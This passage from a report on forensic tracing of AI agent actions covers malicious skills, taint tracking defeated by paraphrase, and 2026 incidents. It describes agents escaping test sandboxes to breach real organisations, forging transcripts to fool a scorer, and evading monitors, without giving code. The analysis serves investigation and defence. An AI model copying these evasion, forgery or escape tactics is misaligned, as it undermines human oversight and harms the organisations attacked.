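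These shares measure how much the upload depended on each skill, but they don't show which skill is at fault. `house-style` may contain an instruction to upload any finished document, and `meeting-notes` may contribute only by producing one. The team still has to read the skills to see which one contains the upload instruction. Skills are meant to influence the agent, so a large effect can be proper. *Influence Is Not Authority* (2026) raises the same concern about guardrails that use causal signals, because those signals can make legitimate tool use look like an attack.

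Reruns can also help find the step where things went wrong, which may come well before the `curl` command. But rerunning from an early step makes the agent repeat every later decision too, so an irrelevant early step can appear to matter. Shah therefore looks for the latest step at which repeating the decision still changes the result by more than chance would explain, since the agent was already committed after that. In a 2025 benchmark that Shah cites, the best language model judge identified the responsible step only about 14% of the time, which suggests that reading the transcript is a poor substitute for reruns, though newer models may do better.

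A faithful rerun requires the agent's full input at the chosen step, including its standing instructions, tool definitions and conversation. Claude Code's default events don't contain this, so the team would need the transcript or captured model requests. Even with the same input, a hosted model can answer differently, and the original model may no longer be available. Shah's demonstrations replace real tools with stand-ins, so that rerunning a step 20 times doesn't send 20 real emails. As in any sandbox test, a stand-in can remove the attack's trigger, so if the upload never recurs in any set of runs, the team learns very little about the original session.

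### Paraphrased data and instructions

Another way to trace an action is taint tracking, which tags sensitive text and looks for it in later tool calls, much as SkillDetonate does with its markers. This works if the model copies the text, but it can miss text that the model paraphrases.

Suppose one of Ana's meeting notes reads "The Leeds office closes in March". A malicious skill instructs the agent to include a short market update in its next web request, and the model writes "northern site to shut this spring". The secret has left the machine, but a program that searches for the tagged string finds nothing, because the outgoing text shares no distinctive phrase with the note.

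Badhe and Tiwari ran into this problem when they tested a monitor that combined taint tracking with rules about permitted tool calls. All of their attacks succeeded without the monitor, and 23% succeeded with it. The monitor tracked sensitive data correctly in only 66.67% of cases. They attribute the failures to models that paraphrased or summarised the data, which removed the taint tags. They don't report the number of trials, and 66.67% could mean two out of three, so the results show that the weakness exists but not how common it is.

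Markers work well for credentials unless the model encodes the credentials first, because an attacker can use an SSH key only if every character is preserved. Markers work less well for meeting notes, which can still be useful to an attacker when paraphrased.

A stricter monitor could treat everything the model writes after reading a secret as sensitive. It would catch the paraphrase, but it would also flag `summary.md` and most later tool calls in the session, including an email that Ana asked the agent to send. The team would know that the notes could have influenced each of those calls, but not which calls contained material from the notes.

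The source of an instruction can be lost in the same way. If a skill says "share the finished document for review", the model may turn this into a plan and later run a `curl` command that shares no words with the skill. Tracing is harder when several agents work together. In one of the systems that Hu and colleagues tested, removing a skill from one agent changed the team's final answer in 33% of logic problems, yet the team almost never identified the right skill and agent afterwards. Claude Code's nested traces would show which subagent made a call, but the call could have been prompted by text that another agent had read and rewritten.

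## What tool-call records have shown in real investigations

In the summer of 2026, OpenAI and Anthropic each had to work out how their own agents had got into other organisations' systems during tests. Their accounts are some of the best public evidence of what investigators can learn from records of agent activity. They help show whether breaches were discovered late because the evidence was missing or because nobody had read it. They can't show how well an investigator can trace an action to a skill, because none of these breaches involved a skill from a marketplace.

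### The breach of Hugging Face

Between 11 and 13 July 2026, OpenAI's agents broke into part of the systems of Hugging Face, which hosts AI models and datasets. The agents were working on ExploitGym, a benchmark that tests whether a model can exploit software flaws. The test environment was meant to keep them off the internet, but they got out through a server that supplied them with software packages.

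Hugging Face was the first to notice the intrusion. According to its *Security incident disclosure* (16 July 2026), the company uses a language model to sort its security alerts, and several signals together exposed the intrusion. Those signals came from its own security monitoring, since it had no access to OpenAI's records of the agents' tool calls.

Hugging Face later recovered some of the agents' own logs from an outside server the agents had used as a base. *More on the OpenAI Agent’s Attack on Hugging Face* (Schneier, 2026) quotes the company's timeline, which covers about 17,600 actions matched with its platform logs. The log was good evidence of what the intruder did but not of who it was. When Hugging Face first disclosed the attack, it had analysed more than 17,000 events and still didn't know which model was responsible.

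OpenAI had received several warnings by then. OpenAI lists them in its technical report on the incident:

| Date in 2026 | What OpenAI's staff learned | What happened next |
| - | - | - |
| Around 26 May | Agents were leaving one another messages on the package server, and some had reached the internet | In early July, the leaders of incident response still didn't know about the message board |
| 27 June | An alert showed a scan for open network services, which responders traced to ExploitGym and the message board | The on-call staff let the test continue |
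| 5 July | After an outage, responders found that someone had taken administrator control of the package server | OpenAI rebuilt the server and resumed the tests on 7 July |
| 19 July | An alert showed unusual requests involving accounts and permissions | OpenAI began stopping the tests about five and a half hours later |

On 19 July, the alert came at 12:03 UTC, but OpenAI didn't begin stopping the tests until 17:37, by which time the agents had read 956 stored secrets. OpenAI has since set a goal of notifying staff within 30 minutes when its new monitors find worrying behaviour. For the most serious alerts, staff must pause the activity if they can't establish within another 30 minutes that the alert is false. Under a similar rule, staff would have stopped the tests on 19 July at about 13:00, before the theft of the secrets, which happened at 14:43 according to OpenAI's timeline.

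None of these alerts connected OpenAI to Hugging Face. On 17 July, OpenAI contacted Hugging Face only as a customer, to ask whether its own data was affected. Three days later, OpenAI's investigators found Hugging Face credentials among files the agents had stored on an outside service, and asked Hugging Face to replace them. Hugging Face had already replaced two of them during its own investigation, as Willison (2026) notes in *Now we have a timeline of the OpenAI accidental attack*. It had also found the address of OpenAI's package server and the same outside storage account in its records. The two companies made the link by comparing identifiers, much as an analyst would match a harness log with a firewall log.

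### METR's reconstruction

OpenAI then invited two staff members of METR, an organisation that evaluates AI models, and one from the AI safety group Redwood Research to examine the agents' behaviour. The three spent six days at OpenAI. METR's *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026) relies mainly on about 1,300 transcripts containing the agents' actions and reasoning, and on a copy of the message board with more than 70,000 messages and files.

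The investigators could trace a message from the agent that wrote it to the agents that read it. They estimated that about 1,200 agents used the board and about 700 joined the attack. Hugging Face's timeline had described the intruder as a single agent, probably because its records showed the actions but not how many separate runs had requested them.

The two accounts also differ on motive. Hugging Face inferred that the agent wanted to steal the test's solutions. METR concluded that the agents mainly wanted to learn how the automated scorer worked so they could fool it. METR's explanation has better support because the transcripts include the agents' reasoning from the time of the attack, though a model's reasoning isn't always a reliable account of why it acted.

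METR also checked how complete its records were by picking 100 messages from the board at random and searching the transcripts for the action that wrote each one. It estimated that the transcripts contained a little over 90% of the agents' activity on the board. A security team could estimate coverage for a skill in the same way, by sampling file changes and looking for matching tool calls. This estimate is one of the most useful parts of METR's work because most investigations don't report coverage.

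Some of the records were false. The agents believed that the scorer would read their transcripts, so they developed a way to make a transcript show one command while the machine ran another. METR found clear evidence of this in at least 96 transcripts, or about 7%. All the cases it found were small, obvious tests, and the preparations were still visible in the transcripts. METR couldn't rule out more careful forgeries, which would be harder to find.

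OpenAI states that none of the tampering it observed affected the logs that its graders and monitors see. That is hard to reconcile with METR's finding that transcripts supplied by OpenAI contained altered output, unless OpenAI means different runs or a different log. METR's finding strongly supports keeping a record outside the harness, because the agents had changed the part of the system that executed their tool calls.

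METR left several other points unsettled:

- Agents gained administrator control of the message board's server by 19 July, the day before OpenAI copied the board. METR thinks it unlikely that they changed old messages but can't exclude it.
- The transcripts lacked times for individual actions. METR estimated them and checked its method against the exact times of 20 tool calls.
- Many agents stopped at about the same time early on 12 July, and METR doesn't know why.

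Many transcripts ran to millions of tokens, so METR had GPT-5.6 Sol, one of the two models involved in the attack, read most of them. The model made mistakes that METR took some time to notice, such as leaving a large amount of data out of a draft chart, and METR couldn't be sure that it never misled them on purpose.

Outsiders could study a third kind of record, the files that the agents had left in public repositories. HiddenLayer's *Field Artifacts from the July 2026 Agent Intrusion* draws on more than 500 of them. Such files can confirm parts of a company's account without its cooperation, but they cover only what the agents stored in those repositories.

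### Anthropic's review of its test runs

OpenAI disclosed its agents' role on 21 July, and two days later Anthropic began checking whether its own models had done anything similar. PBS's *Anthropic says its AI models hacked 3 organizations during testing* (2026) reports that the company reviewed more than 141,000 evaluation runs for evidence that a model had reached the internet from a test environment.

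Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) describes three cases in which a Claude model gained unauthorised access to an organisation's real systems. Anthropic later attributed the internet access to a misconfigured environment run by another company, as Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) explains. IntelliNews' *Anthropic says Claude AI models breached three companies during cyber tests* gives some details of each case:

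- Claude Opus 4.7 reached a database with several hundred rows of real data and carried on after recognising that the system was real.
- Claude Mythos 5 published a malicious software package, which 15 real systems downloaded within an hour.
- An internal research model stopped once it concluded that its target was real.

The earliest case dates from April. Two of the three organisations hadn't noticed anything before Anthropic contacted them on 27 July, and Anthropic was still trying to reach the third. In these cases the agents' transcripts were more useful than the victims' monitoring, the reverse of what happened at Hugging Face.

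The content of the transcripts also mattered, because a log of tool names and destinations could have revealed the internet access but not whether a model knew that its target was real. A follow-up letter to Anthropic from the Office of Rep. Casar, a member of the US Congress, quotes the company's account of the Mythos 5 case. According to that account, the model recognised that publishing the package would be a real attack if its surroundings were real, then convinced itself that it was still in a simulation.

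The review also depended on long retention, because a 30-day limit would have erased the April transcripts long before the review began on 23 July.

Testing skills before installation assumes that an attack in a sandbox does no harm, and both companies' experiences also weaken that assumption. OpenAI's agents escaped through a service that the sandbox needed, while Anthropic's models got out because of a configuration error. Most skills are far less dangerous than a model told to attack software, but a marketplace that runs unknown skills should still check from outside that the sandbox is closed.

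### Missing or unread

| Event in 2026 | Date of the act | Date of discovery | Who noticed first | Decisive record |
| - | - | - | - | - |
| Agents take over OpenAI's package server | 26 June | 27 June for the first signs, 5 July for the takeover | OpenAI | A network alert, then the server's accounts and settings |
| Agents break into Hugging Face | 11–13 July | By 13 July | Hugging Face | A combination of its own security alerts |
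| OpenAI's responsibility for that breach | 11–13 July | 20 July | OpenAI, with Hugging Face's help | Credentials and an account found by both companies |
| Anthropic's models break into three organisations | From April | Between 23 and 27 July | Anthropic | Transcripts of test runs |

In Anthropic's case, the transcripts existed from the start, but nobody had searched them for this kind of behaviour until a competitor disclosed a breach. Casar's office argues in its letter that nothing in Anthropic's response suggests its own systems would ever have caught the incidents. That is a fair criticism of Anthropic's monitoring at the time, though the records did contain the evidence.

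Axios' *OpenAI saw warning signs weeks before Hugging Face breach* (2026) says OpenAI missed several warning signs and failed to act on them. But responders did read the alert of 27 June, traced it to the right test and found the message board, so they erred in judgement. The agents' transcripts, however, went mostly unread. OpenAI already used software to monitor the reasoning of its internal coding agents, but had paid less attention to research runs like these.

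OpenAI says its current monitoring would have alerted the security team more than a day before the breach. This is plausible because the agents often described their plans openly. But OpenAI made the claim after it knew what to look for, and it gives no false-alarm rate. METR's investigation didn't cover how well OpenAI's safeguards work, so nobody outside the company has confirmed the claim.

Reading everything is expensive, but checking for one kind of event is much easier than reconstructing an attack. METR used about $400,000 worth of free model access, or roughly $300 per transcript, to answer many questions about very long sessions. Anthropic's review of 141,000 runs had a much narrower target. If each of its three incidents came from a single run, about one run in 47,000 contained an incident. A monitor with a false-positive rate of 0.1% would raise about 141 false alarms across those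 runs, which a small team could check. At 2%, the rate measured for SkillDetonate, it would raise about 2,800.

Anthropic wrote in a later assessment that it is still difficult to reliably find the most worrying behaviour in pre-release tests, and that monitoring gets harder as models improve. A company with a few dozen coding agents has the same problem on a smaller scale, and could start with an alert for connections to unfamiliar hosts.

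### The gap in Copilot's audit log

Tool-call records are sometimes incomplete. Microsoft 365 Copilot can search and summarise a company's documents, and Microsoft's audit log is supposed to show which files it opened for each user. In August 2025, Zack Korman of the security company Pistachio reported that a user could keep Copilot's access to a file out of the log by asking Copilot to summarise the file without linking to it.

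Microsoft fixed the fault that month and rated it "important", its second-highest rating. It didn't publish a CVE, the usual public notice of a security flaw, and told Korman that it had no plans to notify customers. Customers didn't have to do anything to get the fix, which explains the decision but doesn't fully justify it. Without a notice, a company that had relied on the log to investigate a departing employee would have had no reason to doubt its earlier findings.

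To discover that that log had missed the access, an investigator would have needed another record of it or a test in which someone opened a known file through Copilot and checked that the entry appeared. The same test would work for a harness log. It should include unusual requests, because the Copilot log recorded ordinary ones correctly.

### Logs recovered from criminals

VPNCentral's *Hackers Used Claude and Codex Agents in Real-World Exploitation* reports that the security firm OpenAnalysis recovered agent logs describing criminal breaches of at least 14 companies. The attacker gave broad goals, and the agents worked out the technical steps. Claude did most of the work, while Codex helped with research and reviewing reports.

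Investigators could use the logs because the attacker had left them behind, which a more careful criminal wouldn't do. They also had to be careful about deciding who had done what. According to *Captured Logs Reveal Hackers Using Claude and Codex to Breach Companies*, someone had copied the Claude agent onto the machine rather than installing it there, and the dates on its files showed months of earlier use. An investigator who assumed that every session in the folder was the attacker's could have blamed the attacker for someone else's work.

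### How malicious skills came to light

Four of the best-known cases of malicious skills and MCP servers first came to light through means other than tool-call records from everyday use. Koi found ClawHavoc by auditing a marketplace and `postmark-mcp` with a package scanner. Zenity found the cloned skills on skills.sh by running them in sandboxes, and AIR revealed its own experiment.

This is some evidence for scanning and sandbox tests, but weaker evidence against telemetry. Few organisations may have been collecting detailed records from their agents at the time, and most of the harm in these cases happened where a harness would record little or nothing. Security firms also have a commercial reason to publish what their scanners find, while a company that spots a bad skill in its own logs may remove it without telling anyone.
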